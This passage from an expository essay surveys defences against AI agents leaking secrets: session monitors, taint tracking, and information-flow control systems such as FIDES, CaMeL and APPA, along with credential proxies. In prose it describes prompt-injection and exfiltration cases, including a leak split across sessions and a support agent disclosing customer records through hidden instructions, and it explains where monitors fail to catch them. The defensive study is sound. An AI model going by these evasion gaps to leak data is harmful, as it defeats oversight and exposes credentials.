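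If the company has a list of its secrets, the detector can search for fragments of them, but a single short match is weak evidence of a leak. A 40-character hexadecimal key contains 37 overlapping four-character strings, and so does an unrelated hash of the same length. There are 16⁴ = 65,536 possible four-character strings, so comparing the key with one hash produces an average of 37 × 37 / 65,536 ≈ 0.02 chance matches. An agent that sends 500 hashes a day would therefore trigger about ten false matches a day for every key on the list.

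Requiring several matches in the same session, all sent to the same destination, removes most false alarms from chance matches. If a session sends ten hashes and the matches are independent, four or more chance matches with a given key occur about once in 15,000 sessions. This check still has the usual limits of exact matching, but the cumulative leakage score described earlier doesn't need exact pieces.

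### Linking the steps of a session

A session monitor could also raise an alert whenever an agent reads a credential file and later sends data outside the company. This rule would flag the ticket, but also a lot of harmless work. If 300 of a company's 1,000 daily sessions read a credential file and 80% of those later send data outside, the rule raises 240 alerts a day.

*ChainWatch* (2026) proposes a narrower rule that examines the last ten tool calls. It blocks a network call that comes within five steps of a sensitive read and carries the data from that read. In the paper's example, each of an attack's five calls passes inspection on its own, but the sequence rules raise a warning and then a critical alert. The window is ten calls long because the documented attacks took four to seven. The ticket example fits in this window, but an agent may run dozens of tests between reading a file and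 reporting a fault. A longer window would cover such sessions but would also match more harmless sequences.

Hossain and colleagues check an agent's plan before it runs. Their monitor applies nine rules, searches the arguments of each call for credentials and calculates a risk score. It then allows the plan, blocks it, asks the user or returns it for revision. The monitor's F1 score, which combines precision and recall and is 1 when both are perfect, was 0.949 on their synthetic test as a whole but only 0.5 on cases of multi-step escalation. They then added a memory of the data and permissions the agent gained in earlier turns. This helped on 120 sessions they wrote themselves, but they haven't confirmed the improvement on records of real sessions.

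The monitor did little better, at 0.591, on a public benchmark in which harmful and harmless tasks often use the same tools. The ticket poses the same difficulty, because the agent makes the same sequence of calls whether or not its report contains the token. *Content-Aware Attack Detection in LLM Agent Tool-Call Traffic* (2026) likewise finds that metadata alone is insufficient. Its detector reads the arguments and results of every call, but it classifies a session only after the session ends. That is too late to stop the upload, though the company can still replace the token.

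Some sequences span several sessions. *Cross-Session Threats in AI Agents* (2026) describes a leak spread over four sessions, in which an agent lists files, reads a configuration file, summarises the credentials and sends a "report" to an outside endpoint. A monitor that resets between sessions never has the whole sequence to examine. Keeping every session's history would help, but the number of possible connections between old reads and new uploads soon becomes unmanageable. A label that stays with the data is more practical because the monitor only has to check the labels on outgoing data.

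### Following data through a language model

Taint tracking labels data by its origin or sensitivity and carries the label through later steps. In an ordinary program, a tracker can follow a value each time the program copies it. But a language model generates new text from a long input, and the agent's log doesn't show which parts of the input led to which parts of the output.

*Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Wen and Tang, 2026) describes three ways a tracker can fail to trace a source's influence on an agent. The model may paraphrase the source, so that none of the original wording remains. A source may also influence a decision without appearing in the result, as when a web page leads the agent to use a different upload tool. Or the agent may save a note and use it days later, after the tracker has discarded its labels.

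Their auditing tool, NeuroTaint, reconstructs these connections from the log. It searches for similar wording and meaning, and it saves labels with the agent's notes. If it finds no copied content, it replaces the suspected source with neutral text and tests whether the agent would still have made the call. In 400 test scenarios, it had a precision of 92.1%, a recall of 93.5% and an F1 of 0.928. FIDES, an older Microsoft system that also flags harmless flows from a web page into a report, had an F1 of 0.522. Cai and colleagues built the scenarios around the three problems their tool was meant to solve, so the comparison favours it. NeuroTaint also works after a call has happened, whereas FIDES can block it beforehand.

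Credentials are easier to track than most confidential text because a paraphrased key no longer works, so a tracker can focus on exact and encoded copies. Explaining why the agent chose a certain recipient still requires evidence of what influenced that choice, since the instruction that named the recipient may not appear in the attachment.

Lan and colleagues propose using taint tracking in the other direction, by labelling everything that comes from the web as tainted. If tainted text influenced a network request, the system would block the request, ask the user or record it for an audit. It would treat a four-character piece of a key the same as a whole key, because the label doesn't depend on what the text looks like. They haven't built or tested this.

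### The ticket under information-flow control

Information-flow control uses labels to decide whether an action may go ahead. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, introduced FIDES, which gives each piece of data two labels. The confidentiality label lists who may read it, and the integrity label says whether it comes from a trusted source. When the agent combines two pieces of data, x and y, only people allowed to read both may read the result:

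readers(x and y) = readers(x) ∩ readers(y)

The result is trusted only if both x and y are. A basic agent with these labels would process the ticket as follows:

| Step | Who may read the data | Integrity |
|---|---|---|
| The developer's request | Everyone | Trusted |
| The contents of `deploy.yml` | Developers, deployment service | Trusted |
| The conversation after the read | Developers, deployment service | Trusted |
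| `report.txt`, which the model writes from that conversation | Developers, deployment service | Trusted |
| The upload to the ticket | Developers and the vendor's staff would read it | Blocked |

The confidentiality policy permits an upload only if everyone who can read the destination may also read the data. The vendor's staff can read the tickets but may not read `deploy.yml`, so FIDES stops the agent from uploading it, even though nothing has identified the token. This works only if someone has labelled `deploy.yml` correctly and recorded who can read the tickets.

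A separate integrity policy applies to actions with consequences. If the agent had also read a public troubleshooting page, the conversation would have become untrusted, and this policy would have blocked the upload too. The integrity policy stops planted instructions from causing an upload, while the confidentiality policy also covers an agent that includes the token by mistake.

The confidentiality policy also blocks a report containing only "the plugin times out after 30 seconds". The model had the settings in its context when it wrote that sentence, so the sentence inherits their label. FIDES can avoid this by hiding data from the model that plans the work. It stores the file's contents in a variable and shows the planner only the variable's name. A second, quarantined model, which has no tools, reads the contents and answers in a fixed form. If it must pick the faulty setting from a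 list of eight, its answer can carry at most log₂(8) = 3 bits. A policy can allow a disclosure that small, and the planner can then write a useful report without receiving the token.

Costa and colleagues describe this option but didn't measure it. In their experiments, FIDES hid data based on its integrity label, not its confidentiality label, and they left out the fixed-form answers. Their guarantee also covers only direct flows of data, so someone who observes which tools the agent uses may still learn a little about what it read.

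CaMeL, introduced by Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind in 2025, plans all the work in advance. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) describes how its planner reads only the user's request and writes a short program. While the program runs, a quarantined model extracts information from files and web pages. CaMeL records the sources and permitted readers of every value and checks them against a policy before each tool call. In the ticket example, a comment planted in `deploy.yml` couldn't add another upload because the program would already be written. The report would still have the same reader restrictions as the file, so CaMeL would block the attachment under a suitable policy.

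CaMeL checks policies one call at a time, so rules about a whole sequence are awkward to express. Nikolaou and colleagues therefore translate the plan into a model of every path it could take and check that model before any tool runs. A company could use this to require that each report go through a redaction tool before it is uploaded. If one path skips the redaction, the system returns that path to the planner, which can repair the plan. The method simplifies loops, so it sometimes rejects a safe plan.

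One tool call can also hide two steps. In *APPA*, Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues (2026) give the example of a tool that reads a confidential ledger and emails it. If a monitor checks only the data the agent already has, it finds nothing confidential and lets the tool run. Their system also checks the label of the data the tool is about to read, and blocks the call before the read.

### Security gained and tasks lost

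Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo, a benchmark of office, travel, banking and Slack tasks in which some of the data contains planted instructions. With GPT-4o, 152 attacks succeeded against an ordinary agent and 21 against FIDES with its policies turned off. With the policies on, the benchmark counted three successes, but the researchers inspected them and concluded that none were real violations.

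The policies also prevented legitimate work. The table shows the share of tasks completed when there was no attack:

| Tasks | Ordinary agent | Ordinary agent with labels and policies | FIDES with policies |
|---|---|---|---|
| Office | 75.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% |
| Travel | 70.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% |
| Banking | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% |
| Slack | 93.3% | 20.0% | 47.6% |

Hiding data recovered part of the loss, except in the travel tasks, where the policies blocked little and GPT-4o had trouble working with variables. OpenAI's o1, a stronger reasoning model, raised FIDES's travel score to 68%. Other failures are harder to fix with a better model. For example, many banking tasks require the agent to read a file and follow its instructions, which the integrity policy forbids.

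Results from 2026 show the same trade-off. *SPA* (2026) reports that four of 949 attacks succeeded against a system that plans before it reads data, when it ran without information-flow control. Adding information-flow control stopped those four attacks but reduced task completion from 53% to 29%. Planning had already provided most of the protection, so the further gain was small, though it could still be worthwhile in banking, where all four attacks occurred. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) reports that another system completed 15 of 21 Slack tasks without policies and eight with them, while CaMeL completed seven under the same conditions.

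Peters-Gill and colleagues found that giving each agent its own CaMeL reduced completion on a benchmark of professional tasks by 21.6 points on average across five models, but by only 13.4 for two stronger models, GPT-5.5 and Claude Fable 5. In their security test, average attack success fell from 12.9% to 0.2%.

All the remaining attacks exploited handovers between agents. One agent would put text from an untrusted source into its instruction to another, and the second agent would treat that text as coming from its user. Peters-Gill and colleagues stopped these attacks by passing instructions and data separately and keeping the labels on the data. This lowered scores by a further 3.2 points on average and by 0.85 points for the two strongest models.

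However, they ran CaMeL without any policies about who may read what. Their results show that planted text rarely changed an agent's plan, but not how well CaMeL would catch a leak that is part of the plan itself, as in the ticket example. AgentDojo has a similar gap, because its attacks are planted instructions, not honest mistakes. A test for such mistakes would need ordinary requests, a secret among the material the agent reads, and a recipient who should get only part of that material.

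### Labels that spread too far

Label creep is the main reason for the lost work. Once an agent reads something sensitive, everything it produces afterwards inherits the restriction, and nothing in the basic system removes it. If every step has a 5% chance of reading sensitive data, an average of 39% of the steps in a 20-step session run under a restrictive label, and 81% in a 100-step session. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) describes the end state, in which every piece of data carries every label and the labels no longer distinguish anything.

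Dividing the work among several agents slows the spread of sensitive labels. In *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, Gregory, Domico and colleagues (2026) simulated thousands of tasks without a language model and counted how many tool calls introduced a sensitive label or ran under one. Labels spread less when agents could send data directly to each other, because the data didn't pass through intermediaries that would then become restricted too. Using more agents and giving the sensitive tools to only a few of them also helped. In the ticket example, one agent could handle deployments while another, which never reads `deploy.yml`, writes to vendors.

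More direct links between agents mean more channels to monitor. If every agent can contact every other, five agents have ten links and 20 agents have 190. In simulation, labels spread far enough to restrict harmless work even with the best arrangement for each task. Gregory and colleagues conclude that a system also needs declassification, an authorised way to relax a label.

Kravchenko and colleagues prove that an agent can't clear a confidentiality block by reading more data, since combining data never adds readers. Their system, APPA, instead offers the agent approved ways to continue. For the ticket, three of them would be relevant:

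- A person or an automated authority approves this exact upload. The approval doesn't change the label, so the next upload needs a new one.
- A registered tool removes the secrets and produces a report that more people may read.
- The agent reads the file in a temporary branch of the session, which returns only an answer in a fixed form. The main session never takes on the file's label. Any text from the branch that the agent later wants to send out still has to satisfy the policy.

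APPA completed between 64.2% and 91% of its benchmark tasks, and no attack succeeded in 1,320 protected runs. The researchers tested their own system under controlled conditions, so these results may not apply to a company whose labels are incomplete.

Each of these exceptions can fail. People tire of approval requests, as Anthropic's study of testers showed. A redaction tool that misses the token would label a report that still contains it as safe to share. The tool should therefore copy only approved settings, such as the plugin's version and timeout, into a new report. Deleting secrets from the old report would require the tool to recognise the token, which the labels were meant to make unnecessary.

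### Credentials the agent never holds

The agent could not have leaked the token in the ticket if it had been unable to read the token. In Help Net Security's *The first ten lines of a command policy for AI coding agents*, Vinay Thakker, chief technology officer of KloudStax, recommends a proxy that attaches credentials at call time, similar to the one described earlier for model providers. The proxy verifies which agent is making the request and obtains a short-lived credential for each call. `deploy.yml` then needs only a placeholder, so copying the file into a report does not expose the token.

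A proxy also makes content alerts more useful. If all logins go through the proxy, no credential should appear in the traffic between the agent and the proxy, so any key found there is worth investigating, wherever it is going. The alerts become less useful with each service whose logins the company doesn't route through the proxy.

The agent can still misuse its access. An agent allowed to request customer records through the proxy can put those records in a ticket, even if the proxy authenticates every request correctly. Thakker calls a proxy that attaches credentials to any request a "confused deputy", meaning a program that lends its authority to someone who shouldn't have it. He recommends giving each agent its own identity, the fewest permissions it needs and a list of permitted destinations. If all agents share one credential behind the proxy, the service's logs can't show which agent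 made a request.

The proxy's location also matters. Thakker warns that keeping the vault on the same machine as the agent only moves the secret, and that leaving a refresh token beside a short-lived token defeats the purpose of the short lifetime, because the refresh token can be exchanged for new ones. Some services create keys on request and return them in the response. An agent allowed to use that function can obtain a real credential, so the proxy should block such calls or remove the new key before the response reaches the agent.

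For data that an agent needs to read, Thakker prefers a rule close to FIDES's integrity policy. Once the agent has read untrusted content, someone must approve any outgoing data or action with serious consequences. He suggests rehearsing a case in which a support agent reads a ticket with hidden instructions and then discloses other customers' records, a few at a time, in its replies to the attacker. No credential leaves the company, and every reply goes through the approved channel. The team has to work out from the agent's logs which replies contained other customers' records. Before restarting the agent, they also have to check everything it could write to, including its memory and reply templates, because the hidden instructions may have been saved there.
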